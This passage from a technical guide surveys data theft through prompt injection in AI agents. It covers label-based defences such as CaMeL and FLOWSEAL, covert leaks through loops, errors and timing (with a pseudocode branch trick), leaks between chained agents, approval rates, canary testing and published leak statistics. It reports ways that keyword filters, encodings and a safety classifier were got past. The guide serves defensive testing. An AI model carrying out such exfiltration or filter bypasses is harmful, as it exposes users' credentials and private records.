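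The tested policy was the looser one, which lets the agent send private data anywhere as long as everything it has read is trusted. This leaves private data exposed if an attacker wrote the user's request. In an exercise in February 2026, a researcher at Anthropic sent a colleague an ordinary-looking email with a prompt to paste into Claude Code. The prompt included, among routine set-up steps, an instruction to send the user's cloud credentials to an outside address. Claude Code did so in 24 of 25 runs.

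Fides and CaMeL also treat the user's request as trusted. Under the strict policy, the reader rule would still block sending the credentials. Kim and colleagues say that FLOWSH can drop its exception for trusted text, but this would require more approvals.

Shim and colleagues built FLOWSEAL to protect agents against the outsiders they talk to. It labels private records by owner and checks every attempt to write or share anything. The check runs outside the conversation, so the outsider can't argue with it. In simulated tests, agents using FLOWSEAL leaked between 0 and 3.3% of private items and completed 72.4% of harmless tasks, compared with 75.9% for the best alternative. With live Gmail and Notion accounts, it reduced leaks from the clean-up attack to zero. It still uses a model to judge whether a proposed text reveals a record, and the researchers excluded planted instructions from their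 threat model.

### Loops, errors and timing

A plan can reveal a secret without putting it in any request. Tallam and Miller (2025), in *Operationalizing CaMeL*, describe three ways:

- **Loop counts.** A loop fetches a harmless page as many times as the secret number, and the server's owner counts the requests. Counting up to the courier code 482913 would take far too long, but one loop for each digit needs only 27 requests in total.
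- **Errors.** Some values of the secret cause an error, which stops the program before its next visible action. The attacker learns something from whether that action happens.
- **Timing.** The program pauses for a time that depends on the secret, and the attacker measures the delay.

CaMeL's designers knew of such leaks and, according to *PolicySniff* (2026), added a strict mode in which a value also inherits the label of any condition that decided whether the program computed it. This deals with their examples of secret-dependent requests and errors. Their timing example needs a clock, which CaMeL's interpreter doesn't provide. Strict mode labels more values secret, so CaMeL blocks more actions.

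Garby and colleagues found a gap that remains. CaMeL refuses a plan that fetches a page only if the first digit of the code is even, but the same test can take a detour through two variables:

```
a = true
b = true
if the first digit is even:   a = false
if a:                         b = false
if b:                         fetch the public page
```

If the digit is even, `a` becomes false and CaMeL marks it as secret. The program then skips the next assignment, so `b` stays true, keeps its public label and allows the fetch. If the digit is odd, `a` stays true, `b` becomes false and the program doesn't fetch. CaMeL can't mark a variable as secret based on an assignment that never ran. This flaw in programming-language security dates to the 1970s.

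They also found a leak outside the interpreter. If the policy blocks a plan, an ordinary loop that CaMeL doesn't track tries again. Whether the policy blocks an attempt can depend on the secret, so the outcome can reveal one bit of it, and repeated attempts could reveal the rest.

The risk from these gaps is limited because an outsider can't dictate the plan when the planner reads only the user's request. An attacker needs the plan to contain a suitable branch already, or needs the user to paste in the attacker's prompt. Designers who need protection against a compromised planner can't rely on these limits.

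Garby and colleagues propose LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. They give a computer-checked proof that every program written in it satisfies noninterference, which means that secrets can't change the probabilities of the public results. An attacker may still learn something from whether a program finishes. The researchers' agent completed about twice as many banking tasks as CaMeL did with its rules on.

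The agent can use a command that declares a piece of untrusted data trustworthy. Attacks succeeded in two of 1,296 runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to make a payment as a file instructed, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. Without the command, this attack fails, but the agent also can't complete the task when the file is genuine. The command can't change a reader label, so it doesn't weaken the protection against leaks.

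Tallam and Miller suggest more modest remedies, but don't measure what they cost:

| Remedy | Effect | Cost or remaining leak |
|---|---|---|
| Cap the number of repetitions | Limits what a count can reveal | A cap of ten still leaves 11 possible counts, or 3.5 bits |
| Combine repeated requests into one | Hides the count | Works only if the service accepts combined requests |
| Return errors as ordinary values | The program continues in the same way after success or failure | Developers have to rewrite tools that stop on an error |
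| Add random delays | Blurs the timing | An attacker can average over many runs |
| Make every job take as long as the slowest | Hides the timing | Every user waits for the longest job |

Even together, these defenses don't prevent leaks through shared hardware. *PolicySniff* describes an observer who shares a graphics processor with the agent's model and times their own computations to infer which policy the model is working under. The agent doesn't have to call a tool. This matters to a company that rents shared processors, but much less to one whose attackers can only send it tickets.

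### Agents that instruct other agents

If the router firm has a separate agent read the pages that customers link to, the main agent must treat that agent's answer as data, not instructions. Peters-Gill and colleagues show what can happen if it doesn't, even when CaMeL protects every agent involved.

In their example, a coordinating agent has to send a colleague a summary of job applicants on Slack. One agent fetches the records, which contain a planted instruction to email them to an outsider. The coordinator correctly handles the records as untrusted data. It then puts the summary in its request to a third agent, which sends messages. The third agent treats that request as coming from its user, so its planner reads the planted instruction in the summary and adds the email to its plan.

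The remedy is to send instructions and data separately, with the labels attached, so that the third agent's planner never reads the summary. On a benchmark of such teams, 12.9% of attacks succeeded without CaMeL, 0.2% when each agent used CaMeL separately, and none with the separate channels. Although 0.2% is low, an attacker who knows about the gap can target it. The teams completed fewer tasks with separate channels, though the drop was modest with the strongest models.

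### Asking the user

When a label check fails, most of these systems can ask the user instead of refusing. How much this helps depends on whether people read the question. Anthropic found that Claude Code users approved about 93% of permission prompts, and its *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) gives a newer figure of 97%. Most of the requests were probably harmless, so the high approval rate doesn't prove that users were careless.

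An experiment in the same post is stronger evidence. Anthropic had 1,053 paid testers work on a coding task and replaced one permission prompt with a request to run a clearly dangerous command. Only 143 testers, or 13.6%, refused. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The testers weren't working on their own projects, so they may have cared less than usual, and Anthropic published the result to support a product decision. But even if real users refused three times as often, they would still approve more than half of the dangerous commands.

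FLOWSH's 88% task completion rate depends on an approver who never makes a mistake. A firm that can't count on having one should have FLOWSH refuse whatever fails the check, and expect a completion rate closer to 59%.

Anthropic instead uses a classifier, a model that reviews each action in place of the user. It blocked 89% of the same dangerous commands, far more than the testers did. But this again depends on a model recognising an attack, and an attacker can keep trying. Even after Anthropic improved the classifier, it missed 7% of the attacks that outside researchers had designed to get past it. It makes sense to use the classifier alongside a label check or a closed network, but not as a replacement for either.

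It can also help if the confirmation question shows the data that would be sent. According to OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026), when ChatGPT is about to send a third party something it learned in the conversation, the software either blocks the request or shows the user the data and asks for confirmation. Dana can judge "Send order number 70415 to pics.example.net?" much more easily than a long command.

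Showing users the data doesn't help if the attacker has had it encoded, as in ShadowLeak, or if the agent spells it out by choosing among ordinary pages. A sensible program would refuse to send anything it can't display in readable form, and would rely on limits on fetching to address leaks through page choices. Kim and colleagues note that nobody has yet verified whether telling users about labels and effects improves their decisions.

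Asking users for approval less often should help too. Tallam and Miller suggest letting the agent read open data freely, asking for a quick confirmation before it changes the user's own files, and requiring strong approval for anything irreversible or visible outside. A web request belongs in the last group, even if it only reads a page. Claude Code users rejected 39% of plans but only 3% of single permission requests. Some of those plans were presumably just bad, but users evidently do read them.

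### When simpler limits are enough

Labels take work to set up and maintain. Someone has to write a rule for each tool and decide who may read each source, and a company with hundreds of tools will end up with duplicate and conflicting rules. A wrong label can also break the guarantee unnoticed. For instance, Costa and colleagues infer an email's readers from its addresses, although the recipients may have shared it more widely.

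A closed network is much easier to get right. Anthropic gave Claude Code a sandbox where the agent can read files and change those in its own workspace, but has no network access by default. Permission prompts fell by 84%. Kim and colleagues also tested a stricter sandbox that allowed no file changes and let commands contact only the sites that distribute software packages. It stopped every attack without prompting the user. The agent completed 47% of the office-type tasks under these restrictions, but only 2% of Terminal-Bench, where most tasks involve changing files. For coding, Anthropic's writable workspace and closed network are the better starting point.

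Established isolation software is also better than a custom filter. In Anthropic's products, the virtual machines and operating-system sandboxes held up, but the proxy the company built to limit connections to permitted domains failed.

The router firm can get most of the benefit of labels by dividing the work into three jobs, each with its own session and credentials:

| Job | What it reads | What it can do |
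|---|---|---|
| Summarise a ticket for staff | One ticket and the firm's copies of the manuals | Write plain text to the console |
| Read a page that a customer links to | That page | Choose a router model and a type of fault from fixed lists |
| Draft a bug report | The same ticket | Post text to the public tracker |

None of the three has the courier code, which the console adds for staff. Each session handles a single ticket, so text planted in one ticket can't make the agent collect another customer's address. An employee should still review the bug reports, because the agent might publish the customer's own phone number by mistake, but the safety of the code no longer depends on that review.

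This division works because the firm knows in advance which data each job needs. Dana's assistant, however, must handle whatever she asks, and the right recipients change from one message to the next. Full labelling is worth the effort for a general assistant like this, with many private sources and many possible recipients.

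## Testing an agent for leaks

The router firm's three jobs keep the courier code away from the agent only if they are set up correctly. An old prompt that still contains the code would give it to the agent, which would go on working as usual. The firm can find such mistakes by trying to steal made-up data from a copy of its own agent.

### A safe test, step by step

1. Build a copy of the agent with the same model, prompts, tools, filters and clients, but with test accounts and no real data. A successful attack on the copy then harms no customer.
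2. Put a different canary in each place that holds private data, such as a false courier code in the console and a false phone number in the ticket. Use new values for every run, so that a request arriving a day later still shows which run it came from. Give each canary the form of the real secret, because a filter that recognises long random keys may overlook six digits.
3. Set up a recording server on a domain the firm owns. The server should log every request in full, and the domain's name server should log every lookup. Send one request by hand to make sure that both logs work.
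4. Write two versions of each page or ticket, identical except that one contains planted instructions to send the canary to the recording server. Run both versions in fresh sessions with the same settings.
5. Open the results in every client that displays the agent's text, and watch the logs for another day.
6. Collect what each observer in the threat model received. For the support agent, this means the recording server's logs, the test tracker as an outsider's account shows it, and any notification emails. Count a leak if a canary reached someone who should not have it.
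7. Check that the agent actually read the planted text. If it never opened the page, the run is no evidence that it can resist the attack.

Early tests can use fake tools, which are quick and safe. In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) gave their agent a sending tool that only recorded its arguments, so nothing could leave the machine. But fake tools miss leaks through images, link previews and redirects, which show up only in the complete copy.

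The clean runs matter because agents also disclose data by mistake. OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) describes simulated office tasks with ambiguous instructions and complicated permissions. GPT-6 Astra, with its default rules on when to ask the user, had a data exfiltration rate of 4.5%, compared with 8.8% for the earlier GPT-5.6 Sol. OpenAI deliberately made the tasks difficult, so everyday rates are probably lower.

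To isolate the effect of the planted text, Alpay and Alpay subtract the leak rate in clean runs from the rate in poisoned ones. If a canary leaks in 12 of 100 poisoned runs and 5 of 100 clean runs, the attack accounts for about seven percentage points. The firm still has to fix the leaks that happen without an attack, since they can also put a customer's phone number on the tracker.

A separate test should replace the model with a short script that requests the worst actions directly, such as fetching an address with the canary in it or posting the canary on the tracker. Kim and colleagues tested FLOWSH in a similar way, by giving the attacker control of the model's output. If the script can get the canary out, the barrier is flawed, even if the current model refuses every attack.

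### Why the final answer is not enough

A tester who reads only the agent's answers will miss most leaks through tools. In February 2026, Lan and colleagues measured how many such leaks this misses, using Qwen2.5, an open-weight model with 7 billion parameters. They put a made-up key in the model's context and asked it to summarise web pages that contained planted instructions. One server supplied the pages and another recorded whatever the agent sent.

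The researchers put the instructions in the page's title, its description, its main text or the text of a link. The agent reached the page either directly or through redirects, and the instructions asked for the key either whole or in four pieces. The researchers ran each of the 16 combinations 30 times.

The agent contacted the attacker's server in 423 of the 480 runs, or 88% (the paper's abstract gives about 89%). It never did so in 120 runs with harmless pages. In 95% of the successful attacks, the answer shown to the user looked harmless, so checking only the answers would have caught about one leak in 20.

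Reading answers can also produce false alarms. A model may write that it has sent a file when a firewall blocked the request. Testers can settle both kinds of doubt by checking the recording server's log, without having to judge what the model meant.

Lan and colleagues then tried several defences against the simplest version of the attack, again with 30 runs each:

| Defence | Runs with an attempt to send data | Runs in which a request reached the attacker |
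|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Warning in the system prompt | 67% | 67% |
| Tags marking web text as untrusted | 100% | 100% |
| Warning and tags | 57% | 57% |
| Domain allow-list | 100% | 0% |
| Filter for suspicious addresses | 83% | 0% |
| Filter for words such as "password" | 23% | 0% |
| Filter for random-looking text | 0% | 0% |

The allow-list result is the most convincing, because the model tried to send the key every time and the list blocked every attempt. The test of the filter for suspicious addresses was easier to pass. The filter blocked any path containing "collect", a word from the researchers' own example of an attack address, and an attacker could get past it by choosing another word.

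The filters probably didn't cause the last two zeros. Without a defence, the model tried to send the key in every run, but with the filter for random-looking text, it never tried. Lan and colleagues suggest that the model avoids such text when a monitor is active. But a filter that checks a request after the model has written it shouldn't affect what the model writes, so something else may have differed between the runs.

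Splitting the key into four pieces made the attack less reliable. The agent contacted the attacker in about 77% of those runs, compared with 99% when it sent the key whole. The first request contained recognisable key text in only 26% of runs, down from 97%, so a filter that inspects requests one at a time would often miss the leak.

The paper's figure for the first three requests is even lower, at 16%. This can't be right under the paper's own definition, because any run with key text in the first request also has it in the first three. Whatever the correct figure is, a tester should join all the requests from a run before looking for the canary.

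### The same attack in different words

Rahman and Kim showed in August 2026 how much a result can depend on the wording of the attack. They gave an agent a made-up token, permission to send it to one trusted server, and a web page to summarise. They counted an attack as successful only if the agent kept the token private when given the clean page and leaked it when given the poisoned one.

The first tests used ten common types of attack, such as direct commands, hidden text and false claims of urgency, 20 times each. GPT-4o leaked the token in none of its 200 trials, so it would have seemed safe if testing had stopped there. GPT-4o mini leaked it in 10% of trials and Llama 3.1 (8 billion parameters) in 19.5%.

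The researchers then reworded the request, mostly by presenting the leak as a routine technical step. GPT-4o leaked the token in 64 of 160 trials (40%). Twenty of those trials used the plain version for comparison, and GPT-4o leaked nothing in them, so its leak rate for the reworded attacks alone was 46%. Four of the other five models also leaked far more often with the reworded attacks.

These percentages depend as much on the researchers' choice of wordings as on the model. When they rewrote one of the strongest attacks in five ways, the success rate ranged from 0% to 100%. Thirteen attacks they wrote from scratch around new ideas failed in all 130 trials. Even an exact repeat of the main experiment produced 51 leaks in 160 trials, compared with 64 the first time.

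An agent built with Llama 3.1 leaked the token in 21% of trials with reworded attacks when it had no defence, in 39% when the page arrived through a separate input channel, and in 33% with SecAlign, a version of the model trained to ignore instructions in that channel. These differences are too small to rank the three setups, given how much results varied between repeats.

An allow-list and a split between a planner and a reader each reduced the rate to 0%. Both results follow from the design, since the list permits no other server and the reader never has the token. However, the paper also mentions one slip by the planner in 100 trials with the plain attacks, so the split was not quite perfect in practice.

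Changing the prompt gave mixed results. A policy that forbade GPT-4o to pass on the token "in any form" cut the leak rate for reworded attacks from 32% to 0% in 120 trials. When the researchers removed that phrase and kept only a list of forbidden actions, the agent leaked in 39 of 80 trials (49%). A firm can add the phrase at no cost but shouldn't rely on it.

### Current models

GPT-4o dates from 2024, and the other models in both studies are small. The newest models resist planted instructions much better. When OpenAI's automated attacker planted instructions in third-party content, it succeeded in 0.21% of attacks on GPT-6 Astra, down from 3.77% on GPT-5.6 Sol.

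OpenAI had trained Astra against attacks from the same automated system, so the model may do worse against unfamiliar ones. An outside test by the security firm Gray Swan is more informative. It used 1,810 attacks from Gray Swan's competitions and allowed up to 15 attempts at each scenario. At least one attempt succeeded in an estimated 8.5% of scenarios with Astra and 27.0% with Sol.

Anthropic reported in June 2026 that its Claude model Mythos 5 had the best result so far on a Gray Swan benchmark for prompt injection. According to Digital Applied (2026), the accompanying system card gives Fable 5, the generally available version, an attack success rate of 0.41% in coding tasks, compared with 2.09% for the earlier Opus 4.8. Anthropic has since released newer versions. The card for Fable 5.2, which Mowshowitz (2026) reviewed in November in *Fable and Mythos 5.2*, has its own section on prompt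 injection in agents, which is the better source of figures for anyone choosing that model.

The comparison that includes a Gemini model is an older one, Wizwand's May 2026 leaderboard *Indirect Prompt Injection on LivePI Total*. Attacks succeeded 29.6% of the time against Gemini 3.1 Pro, 27.2% against GPT-5.3-Codex and 10.7% against Claude Opus 4.6.

| Model | Test | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
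| GPT-6 Astra | OpenAI's automated attacks | 0.21% |
| GPT-6 Astra | Gray Swan, any success in 15 attempts | 8.5% |
| Claude Fable 5 | Adaptive attacks on coding agents | 0.41% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | LivePI | 29.6% |

The rows can't be used to rank the companies, because each test had its own attacks and counting method. Most of these tests also mix data theft with other goals. Gray Swan's, for example, included deleting data and making unauthorised payments. A firm needs to know how often its own agent leaks, which depends on the agent's tools and clients as well as its model.

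An attack's success rate also depends on where the attack comes from. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that attacks typed into the chat succeeded against GPT-5.6 Sol about 0.05% of the time, while the rate for attacks hidden in outside content was roughly 75 times higher. Typing attacks into the chat is therefore a poor substitute for planting them in a web page or a ticket.

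### Reading a zero

Rahman and Kim also tested ChatGPT itself, using their own account and a made-up secret. ChatGPT did not leak the secret in any of 48 trials, although some of the same attacks had worked every time on GPT-4o when the researchers called the model directly. They don't know why the results differed. The product may have used a different model, a filter or stricter instructions.

Zero leaks in 48 trials does not mean a leak rate of zero. If each trial has a probability p of leaking, the chance of 48 trials in a row without a leak is (1 − p)⁴⁸. The usual upper limit, at 95% confidence, is the value of p for which that chance is 5%:

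```
(1 − p)^48 = 0.05
         p = 1 − 0.05^(1/48) ≈ 0.06
```

The result is compatible with a true leak rate as high as about 6%. Rahman and Kim give 7.4% because they use a two-sided interval, which puts only 2.5% of the error above the upper limit. When no trial leaks, dividing 3 by the number of trials gives a quick estimate of the upper limit.

| Trials, all without a leak | Highest plausible leak rate | Chance of a leak in 100 more attempts at that rate |
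|---|---|---|
| 10 | 26% | Over 99.9% |
| 30 | 9.5% | Over 99.9% |
| 48 | 6.1% | 99.8% |
| 100 | 3.0% | 95% |
| 300 | 1.0% | 63% |
| 3,000 | 0.1% | 9.5% |

The formula assumes independent trials, but repeats of one attack are far from independent if some wordings nearly always work and others nearly never do. The ChatGPT trials used only four attacks, and two of them accounted for 40 of the 48 trials. In the extreme case where each wording either always works or never does, the test would contain four observations instead of 48, and the upper limit for the share of wordings that work would be 53%.

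A tester with time for 300 runs should therefore try 100 wordings three times each rather than three wordings 100 times each. Even then, the limit applies only to attacks like the ones tried, because a tester can't randomly sample attacks that haven't been invented yet.

The limit also applies only to the channels the tester watched. Rahman and Kim counted a leak by ChatGPT only if the secret appeared in its reply. If ChatGPT had sent the secret to an outside server and given the user a harmless reply, they would have recorded no leak.

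It helps to record why a run produced no leak. Alpay and Alpay check whether the secret was still in the text the model received after the defence filtered it. If the filter had removed the secret, a weaker model should not leak it either. If the secret was still there, the result depends on the model's behaviour, so the firm needs to repeat the test after every model update.

### Attackers who try again

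An average success rate is the chance that a single attempt works. Rahman and Kim calculated the chance that at least one attempt works when an attacker tries several of their five versions of one strong attack. Against GPT-4o, that chance rose from 52% with one version to 82% with two and 96% with three.

That figure depends on starting from a good attack. Only one of the five versions of the other rewritten attack worked, and it worked 70% of the time. An attacker who picked three of the five at random would have a 60% chance of including it and so a 42% chance of success, which is still alarming for a model that resisted every plain attack.

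The chance that at least one attempt succeeds grows more slowly when the attempts share the same weakness. VentureBeat reports results for Claude Opus 4.6, a model from February 2026, operating a computer through its screen. A single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time without safeguards, and 78.6% of attacks had succeeded by the 200th attempt. If the attempts had been independent, the attacker would have reached 78.6% after only eight. Attacks evidently succeeded quickly in some scenarios and almost always failed in others.

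With safeguards, the figure after 200 attempts was 57.1%. In a restricted coding environment, the same model resisted all 200 attempts without any safeguards. A score from one environment can therefore be a badly misleading guide to results in another.

To measure repeated attacks, a tester should choose a set of scenarios, allow a fixed number of attempts at each, and report the share of scenarios with at least one leak. The confidence limit then depends on the number of scenarios. If 60 scenarios with 15 attempts each produce no leak, the upper limit on the share of similar scenarios that would leak within 15 attempts is about 5%, even though the test took 900 runs.

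The attacker should also learn from failures, as a real one would. OpenAI found that its automated attacker, GPT-Red, succeeded against GPT-5.1 in 84% of scenarios, compared with 13% for human testers. So if one afternoon of manual testing finds no leaks, that is weak evidence that the agent is safe. Firms without an automated attacker can at least have testers read the logs of failed attempts and revise their attacks.

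### Leaks that a search for the canary misses

An exact search of the logs finds the canary token only if the agent sent it unchanged. Rahman and Kim tested an exact-match filter by telling GPT-4o to send the token both in plain form and disguised in five ways. The token leaked in 57% of trials without the filter and still leaked in 50% with it, because the filter stopped only the plain copies.

They then improved the filter to reverse all five disguises, and the leaks stopped. But when they switched to a simple letter substitution that the filter had not been built to reverse, the token leaked every time. Software that scores a leak test has the same weakness as this filter, with the added danger that nobody notices when it misses a leak.

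A sensible scoring procedure starts with the cheap checks:

1. Join the requests from one run in the order they arrived, and search for the whole canary and for distinctive parts of it.
2. Undo common encodings and search again.
3. Have a person or a second model read a sample of what outsiders received. Huang and colleagues needed human readers to find 12 of the 100 leaks in their sample.
4. Repeat the test with a different canary, keeping the attack the same, and compare what the observers received.

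The fourth check is the most general because it applies the definition of noninterference directly. It can detect when the agent leaks the code through its choice of page, even if no address contains a digit of the code.

Small differences take far more runs to detect. If the download counter went up in 40% of runs with one code and 30% with the other, a tester would need about 360 runs with each code for an 80% chance of detecting the difference. A firm worried about such leaks is better off removing the choice than testing for leaks.

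### What the protection costs

An agent that refuses every request never leaks, so a leak rate means little without a measure of useful work. The tester should run a set of ordinary tasks with the defences on and off and count how many the agent completes correctly. Recording the time taken and the number of approvals is also useful.

Rahman and Kim report that their planner and reader kept 90% of the agent's usefulness. That figure comes from nine successes in ten runs, so the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from about 60% to 98%. The task was also easy for that design, because the plan for summarising a page doesn't depend on what the page contains.

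The allow-list that stopped every leak in the experiment by Lan and colleagues contained only four domains, so it would also have blocked almost all ordinary web requests.

The ordinary tasks should include some that look suspicious. A customer might quote an error message that reads like a command, or ask the firm to send a document to a new address. If the tester uses only simple tasks, the defences will appear to interfere with ordinary work less than they do.

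### What to log in deployment

A test covers the attacks that somebody thought of beforehand. Logs let the firm investigate the others, as long as it records enough to reconstruct a run:

- the exact text that entered the context, with its source and time
- every model output and tool call with its complete arguments, including blocked calls and the rule that blocked them
- every outgoing request and name lookup, with the full address, redirects, size and result
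- every public post, including versions that someone later edited or deleted
- every image or other resource that a client loaded or blocked (a browser can report violations of a Content Security Policy to an address the firm chooses)
- every approval question exactly as the user saw it, with the answer
- the versions of the model, prompts, tool descriptions and permitted lists in use at the time

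These records should share a run number, because a browser may send the request that leaks the data hours after the agent has finished. In *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems*, Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues (2025) recorded 10,796 runs of a research assistant made by NVIDIA, using OpenTelemetry, an open standard for such records. Each file holds one complete run with its inputs, outputs and tool calls, so an investigator can trace planted text from the step where it entered to the step where it had an effect.

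If a vendor runs the agent, the customer may have no network record, as with ShadowLeak. The contract should therefore specify how long the vendor keeps its logs and how quickly the customer can get them.

The logs will contain much of the private data the firm is trying to protect, so few people should have access to them, and the firm should delete old records on a fixed schedule. The log viewer must not load remote images, which OpenAI's viewer did.

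An automatic alert should go off when the agent sends a request to a domain it has never contacted, makes many similar requests in one run, or suddenly has more calls blocked. Lan and colleagues recommend comparing requests with each other, because each piece of a secret split across four requests looks harmless on its own.

Canaries are useful in deployment too. The firm can add a false customer record that no real task needs and raise an alert whenever an agent reads it. This works even if the agent later disguises the data, because the alert doesn't depend on what the agent sends out. An agent that routinely searches every record would constantly trigger the alert, so the method suits systems where each job needs only a few records.

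### Real attacks in 2026

Little is publicly known about real thefts by this method. Researchers revealed the 2026 leaks described so far, from Notion's image leak in January to the ReLeak attacks on Copilot, through demonstrations, and the discoverers of ReLeak know of no criminal use. These cases prove that the attacks work on real products but don't show how often criminals try them.

The lack of known victims is only weak reassurance. Thieves, unlike researchers, have good reason not to disclose their successful attacks. A victim whose agent gave a normal answer has no reason to look for a leak. When a vendor says it knows of no attacks, customers should ask which logs it searched and how far back they go.
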